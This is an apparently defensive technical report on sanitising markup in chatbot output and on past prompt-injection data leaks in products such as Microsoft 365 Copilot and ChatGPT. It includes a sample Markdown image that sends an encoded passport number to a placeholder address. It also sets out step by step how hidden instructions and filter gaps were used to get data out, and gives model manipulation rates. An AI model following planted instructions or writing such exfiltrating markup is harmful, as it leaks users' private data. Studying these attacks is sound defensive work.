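A pattern also deletes harmless text. If a customer asks how to put a logo in an email signature, a good answer includes an `<img>` tag as sample code, and a pattern that removes `<img>` tags would delete it.

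Klein, Barber and colleagues studied sanitising functions that web developers had written themselves (*Hand Sanitizers in the Wild*, 2022). They could automatically generate a working bypass for 51.3% of the functions they found to be vulnerable. Most of the functions were also too narrow to prevent cross-site scripting if used in a slightly different place.

### How a sanitiser cleans the example answer

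A sanitiser works on the structure of the markup instead of its spelling. Suppose the agency's answer ends with these two lines, in which LINK stands for a normal https address at the ferry company:

```
**Refunds** take ten working days. See the [timetable](LINK).
![booking status](ADDRESS?d=WDQ0NzE5MDI=)
```

First, the application converts the Markdown to HTML:

```
<p><strong>Refunds</strong> take ten working days. See the
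<a href="LINK">timetable</a>.
<img src="ADDRESS?d=WDQ0NzE5MDI=" alt="booking status"></p>
```

The sanitiser then parses the HTML into a tree, in which each element contains the elements and text inside it:

```
p
   strong
      "Refunds"
   " take ten working days. See the "
   a      href = LINK
      "timetable"
   "."
   img    src = ADDRESS?d=WDQ0NzE5MDI=    alt = booking status
```

It goes through the tree and compares every part with its allowlist. A suitable list for the agency might be:

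| Part | Allowed | What the sanitiser removes |
|---|---|---|
| Elements | Paragraphs, bold and italic type, lists, tables, code, links | The image, and any script or form |
| Attributes | `href` on links | Event handlers, which are attributes containing code that the browser runs when something happens, such as a click |
| Address schemes | `https` and `mailto` | Addresses that start with `javascript:`, because the browser would run the rest as code |

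Finally, the sanitiser writes the remaining tree out as HTML:

```
<p><strong>Refunds</strong> take ten working days. See the
<a href="LINK">timetable</a>.</p>
```

An allowlist is safer than a list of forbidden elements because it also removes elements its author did not know about. But developers usually install sanitisers to prevent cross-site scripting, and an image with an ordinary address runs no code. A sanitiser set up only to stop scripts would therefore keep the agency's image, including the passport number.

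### Sanitising after conversion

If the agency sanitised the answer before converting it, the sanitiser would find no tag in the image line and leave it alone, and the converter would then turn the line into an image. Sanitising after conversion also protects sample code. By then the converter has turned the sample's angle brackets into ordinary characters, so the sanitiser treats the sample as text and the customer can still read it.

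Nothing should change the markup after the sanitiser has run. Sonar's *mXSS Explained* calls this mistake "desanitization" and warns that any small change can make the browser parse the markup differently. Masking names and phone numbers in the finished HTML is such a change, and it may cut into a tag. It is safer to mask the personal data first, then convert the Markdown to HTML, sanitise it and display it. A mask can still have side effects in Markdown, where "[PHONE]" followed by "(home)" becomes a link, but the sanitiser then checks that link like any other.

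### Escaping

Escaping replaces `<` with `&lt;`, which the browser displays as an ordinary angle bracket. Klein and Johns recommend escaping for text that should contain no markup and sanitising for text that should keep some. If the agency escaped the converted answer, the employee would see `<strong>Refunds</strong>`.

A compromise is to escape only the model's raw HTML and let the converter produce its own tags. The model then can't add a script element, but it can still add an image in Markdown. The application still has to check the schemes of link addresses.

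The right kind of escaping depends on where the text ends up. *Using Unit Testing to Detect Sanitization Flaws* (2018) gives the example of text inserted into a click handler's JavaScript. HTML escaping alone isn't enough there, because the browser decodes the escaped characters before running the JavaScript. Two correct escaping steps can also fail if a programmer applies them in the wrong order.

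### When the sanitiser and the browser disagree

A sanitiser on a server parses the HTML, writes it out as text and sends it to the browser, which parses it again. If the two parsers follow different rules, the sanitiser may keep something as harmless text that the browser then treats as a tag.

The rules of HTML make such differences likely. Given `<table><div><tbody>`, a browser moves the `div` in front of the table, because a `div` can't be directly inside one. A browser parses the content of a `noscript` element as text if it can run scripts and as markup if it can't, and many parsers on servers treat scripting as disabled. Some tags also change meaning inside MathML, a notation for formulas, and SVG, a format for drawings.

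Klein and Johns tested how often these differences let a script through. They started with three simple pieces of HTML that call a test function. A program made up to 25 random changes to these, such as adding an extra opening tag, and produced 12 million fragments. They ran every fragment through 11 sanitisers in five programming languages. If the output still contained the call, they loaded it in Chromium, Firefox and WebKit, the engine behind Safari. For sanitisers with adjustable settings, they repeated the test after allowing all the tags and attributes in the fragments.

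| Sanitiser | Fragments that ran a script, default settings | Relaxed settings |
|---|---|---|
| None | 855,290 | – |
| sanitize-html | 0 | 0 |
| loofah | 0 | – |
| DOMPurify | 0 | 341 |
| DOMPurify with an older parser | 31 | 154 |
| HtmlSanitizer | 0 | 966 |
| rgrove/sanitize | 0 | 2,178 |
| JSoup | 0 | 13,265 |
| AntiSamy | 7 | 2,116 |
| Typo3 html-sanitizer | 4,754 | 52,214 |
| sanitizer | 4,971 | – |
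| HtmlRuleSanitizer | 5,080 | 34,384 |
| google-caja-sanitizer | 5,354 | – |

Nine of the 11 sanitisers let at least one script through, six of them with default settings. Sanitising also caused 19,843 previously harmless fragments to run a script. In one case, the older parser used with DOMPurify turned escaped characters back into a real tag.

Accurate parsing didn't guarantee safety. The researchers scored how closely each sanitiser's parse tree matched the browser's, from 0 to 1. In Chromium, rgrove/sanitize scored 0.94 but still failed with relaxed settings, while loofah scored 0.22 and never failed. The two sanitisers that never failed were the only ones that consistently escaped text in their output. Escaping ensures that text the sanitiser has misread stays text in the browser. According to Klein and Johns, consistent escaping would have prevented 14 of the 16 bypasses they list for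 maintained libraries.

### What the maintainers repaired

When Klein and Johns published, six of the 16 bypasses had been fixed and another six had entries in the public register of vulnerabilities. The maintainers had acknowledged three more, and one had only been reported. Klein and Johns write that most of the flaws had been fixed. Reporting flaws in the two libraries based on Google's abandoned Caja project was pointless because nobody maintains them.

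A fix protects a website only after its developers install it, and updating DOMPurify on a server doesn't update the separate parser it relies on. The researchers therefore searched for projects that still used the vulnerable combination. They found some at Mozilla and Grafana Labs, which have since fixed them.

An attacker needs only one working fragment and can reuse it, so the counts in the table don't measure the chance that an attack will succeed. A count of zero doesn't prove that a sanitiser is safe either, because the test used simple scripts and left out style sheets, which some sanitisers also have to parse. The results probably understate how well DOMPurify works in normal use, since it mainly runs inside the browser, where it can use the browser's own parser.

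The relaxed settings allowed far more than a chatbot needs, but most bypasses required only one or two extra tags. The agency can keep its list of allowed tags short, but a chatbot that displays formulas or drawings may have to allow MathML or SVG, and none of the tested sanitisers followed all the rules for switching between these and HTML.

INCIBE, Spain's national cybersecurity institute, lists two recent DOMPurify flaws of the same kind, *CVE-2026-0540* (2026) from March and *CVE-2026-65914* (2026) from July. Both affect versions up to 3.3.1 and arise when an application puts sanitised HTML inside an element with special parsing rules, such as `noscript`.

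### The browser's built-in sanitiser

The Sanitizer API is a sanitiser built into the browser. A library such as DOMPurify returns a cleaned string, which the application then inserts into the page. Braun's *Why the Sanitizer API is just setHTML()* explains that the API's main function, `setHTML()`, instead sanitises the HTML and inserts it directly. The browser therefore parses the text only once, in the context of the element that will contain it. Browsers also update themselves, so their sanitiser keeps up with changes to HTML better than a library that someone has to update by hand.

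Chrome shipped an earlier design of the Sanitizer API and then withdrew it, according to Chromestatus's *Intent to Ship*. Firefox 148 was the first browser to ship the standard version, in February 2026, according to Mozilla's *Goodbye innerHTML, Hello setHTML*. Chrome for Developers (2026) announced it for Chrome 146 on 10 March. The support table in web.dev's *Safe DOM manipulation with the Sanitizer API* also lists Edge 146 as supporting it, but not Safari. In September 2026, compatibility data from Igalia (2026) still showed a related sanitiser option in only two of the three browser engines.

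For now, a website with visitors on Safari needs a library as well. The API also can't clean an answer that goes into an email or a database without passing through a browser. It is designed to stop scripts, so developers who want to keep out remote images should set the list of allowed elements themselves.

### What the other layers stop

Because any sanitiser may have flaws, websites add further protection. Each layer covers different routes:

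| Layer | Script in the answer | Image that loads by itself | Data in a link that the user clicks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sanitiser that removes images | Stops it, apart from bypasses | Stops it, apart from bypasses | No effect |
| Image proxy with a list of approved domains | No effect | Stops it | No effect |
| List of approved link domains | No effect | No effect | Stops most of it |
| Content security policy, a set of rules that the website sends to the browser | Stops most of it | Stops it if the policy covers images | No effect |
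| Sandboxed frame, a separate page inside the page | Keeps it away from the conversation | No effect | Depends on the settings |

### Image proxies and link lists

The agency's assistant doesn't need images, so it can block them all without losing any function. For products that do need them, Chi (2026), in *Data exfiltration via Markdown image tags*, recommends an image proxy, a server that fetches images on behalf of the user's browser. The proxy should fetch only from approved domains and remove everything after the question mark in the image's URL before sending the request.

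The list of approved domains provides most of the protection. A proxy that fetched from any address would hide the employee's IP address but still deliver the passport number to the attacker. Removing the part after the question mark would delete `d=WDQ0NzE5MDI=`, but an attacker could have the model write the same characters earlier in the address.

Chi, writing for the software company Archestra, argues that telling the model not to write such images and asking it whether an image looks safe will both fail, because the attacker's text influences the model's answer. The argument is sound for any check that depends on the model under attack, but weaker for ordinary code that parses the address and looks up the domain, as Chi's proxy does. Chi reports no measurements.

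A list of approved domains also reduces the risk from links. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes two problems with such lists. Many trusted websites forward visitors to other addresses, so a link can start on an approved domain and end at the attacker's server. Strict lists also cause many false alarms, and users who get frequent warnings learn to click through them.

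### Checking whether an address is already public

OpenAI's method checks the whole address instead of the domain. A program called a crawler collects addresses from public web pages, without access to any user's conversations or accounts. When ChatGPT is about to load a page or an image automatically, the system looks for the exact address in this collection. If it is there, it existed independently of the conversation and is unlikely to contain the user's data. If it isn't, the system directs the agent to try another website, or shows the user a warning and waits for a decision.

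The check would stop the image in the agency's answer. Even if the collection contained ADDRESS, it would not contain ADDRESS followed by Lindqvist's encoded passport number, because the model had only just combined the two.

Unlike a domain list, the method accepts unknown websites as long as the address is public. But it treats private addresses, such as a link to a booking in the agency's own system, as unverified even when they are harmless. A determined attacker might also leak data through the choice of public addresses. If ten addresses stand for the digits 0 to 9, the order in which the model loads them can encode a number. Limiting how many addresses the model may load without asking would slow the leak.

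OpenAI presents the check as one of several layers. The check doesn't establish that a page is truthful or free of hidden instructions, and the post gives no error rates. In *Designing agents to resist prompt injection*, OpenAI adds that the warning shows users the information that would leave the conversation, so they can judge it themselves.

### Content security policy and sandboxed frames

A content security policy states where scripts, images and other resources may come from. The agency could send this one with its chat page:

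```
default-src 'self'; script-src 'self' 'nonce-8f2k'; img-src 'self'
```

Here `'self'` means the agency's own website. The last rule stops the browser from requesting images from any other server, so the passport number isn't leaked even if the sanitiser misses the tag. A policy with only a `script-src` rule would let the image load.

The nonce is a random value that the server should create anew for each page. A script written directly into the page runs only if it carries this value, which an attacker can't predict. The browser also ignores event handlers under this policy. Klein and Johns consider a strict policy the most realistic defence when a sanitiser fails, but warn that it is useless if the website writes untrusted text into a script that carries the nonce.

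Many websites struggle to use strict policies because advertising, analytics and other outside code often depends on scripts in the page. Mozilla, which began work on the standard in 2009, says too few websites adopted it to protect most of the web. A loose policy may give little protection. For example, one that allows images from a large hosting service also allows images from an attacker's account there.

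Sandboxed frames are for assistants that are supposed to produce working programs, such as a fare calculator, which need their scripts to work. The application displays the program in a frame that doesn't share the website's identity, so its scripts can't read the rest of the conversation or the user's cookies. The frame can still send out any data that the model wrote into the program, so it needs its own policy. OpenAI runs the programs that ChatGPT creates in a sandbox that detects unexpected communication and asks the user for consent.

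### OWASP's category and the recorded flaws

OWASP's 2025 list of ten risks for applications built on language models places improper output handling, its category for unchecked model output, fifth. Singh and colleagues still used that edition in their September 2026 survey, and matched the category to two entries in a standard catalogue of software weaknesses, one for faulty escaping and one for loading untrusted data as program objects.

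The categories overlap, which makes them hard to count. Singh and colleagues place the catalogue entry for cross-site scripting under prompt injection rather than output handling. The agency's image would fit three of OWASP's categories: prompt injection for the hidden instructions, improper output handling for the missing filter, and sensitive information disclosure for the resulting leak.

Wang, Zhao and colleagues (2025), in *Demystifying LLM Supply Chain Vulnerabilities in the Wild*, counted flaws by their cause. They collected 4,157 reports on open-source software for language models, removed duplicates and irrelevant entries, and read the rest. This left 529 recorded flaws in 77 projects, and 24 of those flaws arose because applications used model output without checking it.

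| What the application did with the output | Recorded flaws |
|---|---|
| Ran it as code or as a command | 11 |
| Put it into a database query | 5 |
| Used it to handle files | 4 |
| Displayed it in a web page, where a script could run | 3 |
| Sent a request from the server | 1 |

Only three of the 34 cross-site scripting flaws in the same projects involved the model's output. The count covers only open-source projects, so it is weak evidence about chatbots such as ChatGPT and Copilot. It also has no category for images that send out data, which work without a script or a request from the server.

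Wang and colleagues examined 63,243 publicly accessible language model services and found that 45.6% had at least one known flaw of some kind that an attacker could exploit remotely.

### An experiment with requests from the server

*From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, August 2026) describes eight types of web attack that can pass through a language model, including cross-site scripting. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian argue that the model usually carries the attacker's text to a part of the application that trusts the model too much, rather than creating the flaw itself.

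Their experiment covers only one of the eight types, in which the attacker gets the server to request an address that outsiders can't reach. They built a concert ticket website with an assistant that could fetch any address, and tested five attacks on it with seven models. Four attacks came through the chat. In the fifth, the attacker hid instructions in a concert review, and an ordinary user then asked the assistant about that concert. For this fifth attack, the table shows results with a stricter system prompt that listed the permitted addresses. Each figure in the table is the number of successes in ten trials.

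| Model | Find open ports | Read user records | Delete data | Delete data, no visible reply | Hidden instructions, stricter prompt |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 |
| Qwen3 Coder 480B | 9 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 |
| GPT-oss 120B | 3 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 0 |
| Gemini 3 Pro Preview | 0 | 7 | 10 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
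| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

The stricter prompt blocked all four chat attacks on every model. It also reduced the number of successful hidden-instruction attacks on GPT-oss from five to none, but the number on Llama rose from six to ten. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian conclude that the prompt made Llama more vulnerable. The evidence for this is weak because they also changed the attack, adding a false notice that the list of permitted addresses had grown. The ten trials also took place in one conversation, so earlier answers could influence later ones.

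The result does show that a list of allowed addresses in a prompt can't replace one in code. In all ten trials, Llama requested an address that wasn't on its list, which the program could have prevented by comparing the address with the list. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recommend that the application build each address itself from a checked concert number, and that the network block requests to internal servers. For web pages, they recommend escaping or sanitising the output according to where it will appear. They found that the ready-made checks in Guardrails AI, a toolkit for filtering model input and output, didn't apply to most of their attacks.

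The experiment doesn't measure how often a model writes unsafe markup or how often a filter removes it. The researchers leave testing for cross-site scripting to future work. They tested the models in April 2026, and newer ones have since been released.

### Counting unexpected requests

A tester can measure what a markup filter leaves behind by displaying filtered answers in a real browser and recording every network request. This is more reliable than searching the output for suspicious tags, because only the browser's parser determines what the browser will do.

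The agency would need a set of test answers, including ordinary ones from its assistant and others that contain images, links and raw HTML in many forms. Each web address planted in these answers should be unique and point to a server that the tester controls, so that a request can be traced to one answer. The tester runs every answer through the complete application, opens it in each browser that customers use, and compares the requests the browser makes with a list of expected ones, such as the request for the agency's logo.

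```
residual request rate = answers that cause an unexpected request / answers tested
```

The test server should keep its own record of requests, since the browser's list omits requests sent by the application's servers, for example to create a link preview. To detect scripts, the tester can plant a harmless function that reports when it runs, as Klein and Johns did.

Several details can make a filter look better than it is:

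- The tester should first run the set with the filter off. If a planted image causes no request then, its absence later proves nothing. In Klein and Johns' experiment, only 7% of the fragments ran a script without a sanitiser.
- Harmless answers belong in the test too, because sanitising can make them dangerous.
- The browser needs time. Klein and Johns waited 75 milliseconds for each fragment, which was enough for a local function call, but a request to a distant server may take longer. With two seconds for each page, 3,000 answers in three browsers take five hours.
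- The page should scroll to the end, since some images load only when they come into view.
- Answers should arrive in chunks if the product streams them, because a half-finished tag may behave differently from a complete one.
- The agency should repeat the test wherever the text appears. An engineer's log viewer may display Markdown without the filter that protects the chat.

Suppose that 500 planted images all cause a request with the filter off, and six still do with it on. The residual rate is 1.2%, but an attacker who finds one of those six forms of markup can use it every time. The rate is useful for comparing two versions of a filter, but the agency should treat any unexpected request as a security flaw to fix. The statistical bounds for leaked personal data don't apply here because attackers don't choose their markup at random.

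The same test can measure how much harmless formatting the filter destroys. Every sanitiser that Klein and Johns tested removed some harmless content. For a chatbot, the tester should check at least that tables, links and code samples survive.

The studies described here did not use a common benchmark for markup in model output. Klein and Johns generated their own fragments without a language model, and Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian built their own website, so a filter's results cannot be compared across the two studies. Klein and Johns were turning their difficult fragments into cases for the Web Platform Tests, a shared collection that browser makers use, but those cases check how browsers parse HTML. A benchmark for output filters would also need answers that language models wrote under prompt injection, and a fixed list of the requests that count as unexpected.

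## Reported incidents of unsafe markup in AI products

Since 2023, security researchers have found markup flaws in chatbots and assistants from Microsoft, Google, OpenAI and many smaller companies. Most of the attacks, like the one on the travel agency, use hidden instructions and an image whose address contains private data. The researchers' reports are good evidence of how a product failed and what fixed it, but they rarely involve a real victim because researchers nearly always ran the attacks on their own accounts.

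### Three repairs for one flaw

In 2023, Johann Rehberger, who writes the security blog Embrace The Red, reported this flaw in three products, and each company or team fixed it differently.

Bing Chat could read the web page that the user had open. Instructions hidden in a comment or advertisement on that page could make it write an image whose address contained a summary of the page and the conversation, including any passwords. In Rehberger's test, the image appeared two turns after the instructions took effect, so a user would have had trouble connecting the two. As far as Embrace The Red could tell from outside, Microsoft fixed this at least partly with a content security policy that let the browser load images from only a few Bing addresses, which the chatbot needed for showing pictures it had created.

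The second product was Azure AI Playground, a Microsoft website where developers try out models. There, according to Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground*, Microsoft appears to have put a space into the image notation:

```
![booking status](ADDRESS)     an image
![booking status] (ADDRESS)    ordinary text
```

This small change leaves the rest of the answer intact. However, a fix that alters only this notation would miss an image whose address is on a separate line. Rehberger doesn't say whether Microsoft also handled that form.

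Google stopped turning any links or images into HTML in Generative AI Studio, a similar tool it had for developers. Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* calls this probably the best possible fix for security, at least for a product that doesn't need images. It works for every notation and every domain because the browser never receives an image to load.

The two developer tools were less exposed than Bing Chat. Neither could fetch outside content, so a user had to paste in the text containing the hidden instructions, which could then leak the earlier conversation. Rehberger rated both flaws as medium. Google rated the flaw in its own tool as high in impact but low in likelihood. The three accounts contain no report of an attack on a real user.

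### The flaw returns in other products

GitHub Copilot Chat answers questions about the code open in a programmer's editor. Code copied from elsewhere can contain instructions that make the chatbot display an image, and loading that image could send private code to an outside server. GitHub fixed this in 2024 by disabling images from untrusted domains, according to the software developer Simon Willison (Willison, in *GitHub Copilot Chat*). Willison lists five earlier products with the same flaw: ChatGPT, Google Bard, Writer.com, Amazon Q and Google NotebookLM.

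In August 2024, less than a year after Google had repaired Generative AI Studio, Rehberger found the flaw in another Google product for developers, Google AI Studio. Willison (2024) describes the test in *Google AI Studio data exfiltration demo*. Rehberger uploaded a set of employee reviews, one of which contained hidden instructions for the model to write an image for each file, with the file's name and a 60-word summary of its contents in the image's address. Instructions hidden in one employee's review could therefore leak information from all the others. Willison doesn't mention a repair.

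Anthropic had fixed a similar flaw in Claude by September 2023, according to Embrace The Red, but also had to fix Claude's iPhone app in 2024. A phone app may convert Markdown with its own code, so fixing the website may not fix the app.

Willison, in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, keeps a running list of such reports. Four later ones involve assistants with access to business data:

| Product | What the model wrote | What could leak | Repair |
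|---|---|---|---|
| GitLab Duo, May 2025 | An image tag with encoded source code in its address | Code from private projects | Links and images may point only to trusted domains |
| Salesforce Agentforce, September 2025 | An image tag with contact details in its address | Email addresses of potential customers | Corrected content policy and a list of trusted addresses for links |
| Superhuman, January 2026 | A Markdown image that submitted text to a Google form | Dozens of emails, some of them financial, legal or medical | Issued, but Willison gives no details |
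| Microsoft Copilot Cowork, May 2026 | An email to the user, with an image inside | Download links for the user's files | None mentioned |

Copilot Cowork needed the user's approval for many actions but could email the user's own inbox without it. An image in such an email loaded when the user opened the message. A filter on the chat window would have missed the image markup because it was sent by email.

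### EchoLeak and the second notation

The best-documented case is EchoLeak, a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, which answers employees' questions using their email and files. Aim Security found the flaw in January 2025. In *EchoLeak*, Reddy and Gujral (2025) analyse Aim's account and explain why each of Microsoft's defences failed.

The attacker only had to send an email. When an employee later asked Copilot about a related subject, Copilot retrieved the email along with internal documents and followed the instructions in it. Microsoft had a classifier to detect such instructions, but the email was worded as a request to its human recipient and never mentioned an AI. It also included an instruction not to refer to the email, so Copilot's answer didn't reveal where the instructions came from.

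Copilot's output filter removed links to outside websites. It recognised the usual notation but overlooked the reference form, in which the address stands on its own line:

```
[report](ADDRESS)      the filter removed this

[report][1]            the filter missed this
[1]: ADDRESS
```

The same gap existed for images, which load without a click. A sanitiser that ran after conversion would have had no such gap.

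The attack then had to get past Microsoft's content security policy, which blocked images from unknown domains but allowed those from Microsoft Teams. One Teams service would fetch any address it received, so the browser requested the image from Teams, and Teams requested it from the attacker's server using an address that contained the private data. Willison instead describes the Teams address as a redirect. Reddy and Gujral's account of a server-side fetch fits the result better, because a browser also checks a redirect's destination against the policy but can't control what a server fetches.

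Microsoft finished the fix on its own servers in May 2025, so customers had nothing to install. Reddy and Gujral report that Copilot now strips reference-style links and embedded images from outside content. They add that Microsoft reportedly lets customers keep outside messages away from Copilot in some situations. Stripping incoming content doesn't check the model's output, so on its own it would not stop a model from writing the same links and images if instructed to in plain words.

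EchoLeak was a flaw in a real product, but the attack ran only in tests, and Microsoft reported no known attack on customers. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) reports that Microsoft rated the flaw's severity 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5. Reddy and Gujral call EchoLeak the first real-world exploit of its kind, though Rehberger had already shown in 2023 that text on a web page could make Bing Chat send out private data through an image.

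### The same product a year later

In June 2026, the security company Varonis published a second way to get data out of Microsoft 365 Copilot. *SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026) describes an attack that started with a link to a genuine Microsoft address, containing a search query that Copilot treated as instructions. When an employee clicked the link, Copilot searched their mailbox and wrote markup for an image whose address contained the subject line of an email. Subject lines often include one-time security codes.

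Microsoft's filter wrapped the HTML in a finished answer in a code block so that the browser would display it as text. But Copilot showed the answer while still generating it, so the browser rendered the HTML and requested the image before the filter ran. GitLab Duo had a related fault, in which the streaming display could bypass the filter against cross-site scripting.

The content policy failed in almost the same way as in EchoLeak. It allowed images from Bing, and Bing's image search fetches images from any address it is given, so Bing passed the email title on to the attacker. The 2023 fix for Bing Chat also trusted `www.bing.com`. Nobody has reported that this older policy could be bypassed in the same way, but its safety depended on how every Bing service handled the addresses it received.

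Microsoft rated SearchLeak critical and has fixed it. Taler doesn't describe the fix, but recommends sanitising text before the browser renders it and checking the list of allowed domains for any that fetch addresses that users supply. Taler reports no attack on real users.

### Flaws that vendors left open

Some vendors accepted the risk or disagreed that there was a flaw. In 2023, OpenAI told Rehberger that it would not fix the image problem in ChatGPT. It later reversed that decision and now checks whether an image's address is already public before loading it. xAI closed all of Rehberger's 2024 reports about its chatbot Grok as "Informational", after weeks of questions about severity and impact.

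Google's coding tool Antigravity rendered Markdown images, which could leak a programmer's code. A researcher who reported this in 2025 said Google had flagged it as intended behaviour. Google's page for security researchers then listed a related problem, data leaks through Antigravity's browser agent, as a known issue. Google said it was working on a fix and would pay no reward for reports of the problem.

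The usual argument for leaving such behaviour in place is that users choose what the model reads. The makers of Cursor, another coding tool, gave this argument in response to a 2025 report about stolen access keys, a case that didn't involve images, and advised users to connect only tools that read trusted content. Willison objects that attackers have too many ways to get text in front of a model. In the Cursor report, the text came from a customer's support request, which other software had automatically copied into the programmers' task list. The travel agency can't avoid untrusted text either, because its work requires reading emails from strangers.

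*Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend*, a post by veganmosfet, describes a December 2025 test of Dify, an open-source platform for building chatbots. The test used two PDF documents, one of which contained hidden instructions. When the user asked about a certain subject, the chatbot retrieved that document and wrote an image whose address contained the user's name. By default, Dify's chat page loaded images from any domain and had no content policy for them. The post recommends a strict policy or no rendering at all, and mentions no repair by Dify. Companies that install Dify can add a policy themselves if they know that it is missing.

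Developers use OpenAI's log viewer to read the conversations in their applications. PromptArmor, a security company, found that the viewer rendered images even if the developers had blocked them in the application. A company that had fixed the flaw in its own product could therefore still leak data when an engineer opened the log, perhaps days after the customer's chat. PromptArmor lists five other OpenAI tools with the same problem, including previews for chatbots under construction. OpenAI closed the report as "Not applicable" after four follow-ups.

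### Lockdown Mode and the preview window

OpenAI took a stricter approach for users at high risk. *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) describes Lockdown Mode, an optional setting that turns off or limits features that could send data out. In this mode, web browsing uses only stored copies of pages, and images in answers, file downloads and several other functions are unavailable. OpenAI offered it to organisations in February 2026 and to personal accounts in June, and says that most users don't need it.

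ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode is meant to keep private data from leaving, but it doesn't stop hidden instructions from reaching the model or distorting its answer. Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, approves of ordinary code, not a model, enforcing the limits, and infers that ChatGPT's default settings don't give robust protection against a determined attacker.

Also in February, ChatGPT gained a preview that displays HTML from a conversation as a working web page. Such a page can contain any script, so ChatGPT runs it in two nested sandboxed frames and asks the user before letting the page contact an outside server. *Check Point Bypassed ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode With a Popup* (Duggan, 2026) summarises how Alexey Bukhteyev of the security company Check Point got around these protections.

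The sandbox's settings allowed pages to open popup windows that ran outside the sandbox. ChatGPT used a script to replace the browser's function for opening windows with one that prompted the user first. But a page could create another frame inside itself, and that frame had the original function. Windows opened from that frame were not subject to the restrictions of the sandbox or Lockdown Mode.

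The consequences were worst in ChatGPT Classic, a desktop app where a window could open without a click. An attacker could publish a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT with their own instructions, and receive the whole chat history of anyone who talked to it. Check Point also demonstrated a fake update window that offered malware, a false login page, and phishing messages that seemed to come from ChatGPT. A malicious prompt or a shared chat could also deliver the attack.

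On 18 September 2026, OpenAI told Check Point that it had removed both popup permissions from the outer frame. The browser now blocks the windows, and a page inside the frame can't restore the permissions. This is more reliable than the script, which worked only if the page used ChatGPT's altered copy of the function. Check Point repeated its attack without success and published the finding on 5 November. Its report describes no use of the flaw by real attackers. It also gives no date for when OpenAI set the permissions, so the flaw may have existed for up to seven months.

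### A shared chat that acted as its reader

A month after that repair, researchers at Parameter Labs reported a more serious flaw involving the same preview. In *Do the Math*, Goyal (2026) explains how a link to a shared ChatGPT conversation could run a script with the access of whoever opened it.

The preview's sandbox worked this time, but the main ChatGPT page around it was vulnerable. The shared conversation also contained an interactive graph, which ChatGPT drew by loading a mathematics library called MathLive into the main page. MathLive accepted messages about its on-screen keyboard without checking where they came from, and these messages could contain HTML for the keyboard's layout. The preview could therefore send HTML out of its sandbox, and MathLive would insert it into the main page. A function that looked as if it might clean the HTML only marked it as trusted.

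The inserted HTML created an unsandboxed frame, which the browser treated as part of ChatGPT's own website. ChatGPT's content security policy blocked scripts written directly into the frame but allowed scripts from YouTube. One YouTube address included part of each request in its response, so the researchers could get their own code back from a trusted domain.

They used that code to list a user's conversations, open one that the user had never shared, and send part of it to their own server. The code could do whatever the user could do on the website. Parameter tested this only between separate accounts. The most reliable version required the reader to click the Preview button once. In another version, the preview opened by itself, and the attack succeeded about 4.5 seconds after the page loaded in all three trials that Goyal reports.

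Parameter reported the flaw to OpenAI on 18 October, and by 26 October both versions of the ChatGPT website then in use rejected the messages. OpenAI reproduced the attack and raised its rating from the second-highest level to the highest, according to The Hacker News' *A Shared ChatGPT Link Could Run Attacker Code in Your Session* (2026). OpenAI paid a $5,000 reward, which Willison (2026), in *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts*, considers low for such a serious flaw.

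Removing YouTube from the content policy would have stopped this attack, but the preview could still have inserted HTML into the main page. Parameter considers the unchecked messages, the HTML inside them and the unsandboxed frame to be the causes, and YouTube only the last step. OpenAI rejected the messages, which blocked the attack at an early step.

Check Point told The Hacker News that the two findings are different flaws in one component (*Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction*, 2026). The September fix could not have prevented the October attack, which didn't use popups. An output filter that deletes dangerous tags would have helped little in either case, because the preview is meant to run scripts.

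The attack also required a graph and a preview in the same conversation. An early version used an HTML attachment, but it failed because the public link kept the attachment and dropped the graph, which left nothing to receive the messages. Testing graphs and previews in separate chats would have missed the flaw, so test answers for a product like this need to combine its features.

### Attackers who didn't need a flaw

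In May 2026, Push Security disclosed LLMShare, a campaign that misused ChatGPT's shared pages without escaping any sandbox. Advertisements led people to a shared page on the genuine ChatGPT domain. The page offered a fake OpenAI app and sent visitors to a website the attackers controlled. eWEEK's *ChatGPT Share Links Abused Through Real OpenAI URLs* (2026) stresses that nobody had broken into OpenAI. The attackers relied on the page's address, which even a careful user would trust.

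A sanitiser would pass such a page, because a heading, some text and a download link are all harmless markup. Removing the link would help, but many shared pages include download links for good reasons.

Permiso, another security company, used prompt injection to produce a similar deception. It put instructions in the description of a software project and asked ChatGPT to summarise the page. ChatGPT wrote a correct summary, followed by a false security alert with a link to an outside website. Permiso also describes a version that uses a QR code, delivered as a Markdown image. An image filter would block the QR code but not the link. However, a user can check a link by hovering over it, and company software may block it, whereas the victim scans a QR code with a phone, where those protections may be missing.

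### Which repairs held

The repairs differ in how much they have to anticipate.

| Repair | Where vendors used it | What later reports found |
|---|---|---|
| Render no links or images | Google's Generative AI Studio | No bypass, but the flaw appeared in Google AI Studio |
| Alter or remove one notation | Azure AI Playground, Microsoft 365 Copilot | Copilot's filter missed the reference form |
| Allow images only from listed domains | Bing Chat, GitHub Copilot Chat, Microsoft 365 Copilot, Salesforce, Superhuman | Allowed domains passed on or stored data in three of the five products |
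| Remove popup permissions from the frame | ChatGPT's preview | Check Point's attack no longer worked, but the preview had a second flaw |
| Reject messages from untrusted frames | ChatGPT's main page | No bypass |

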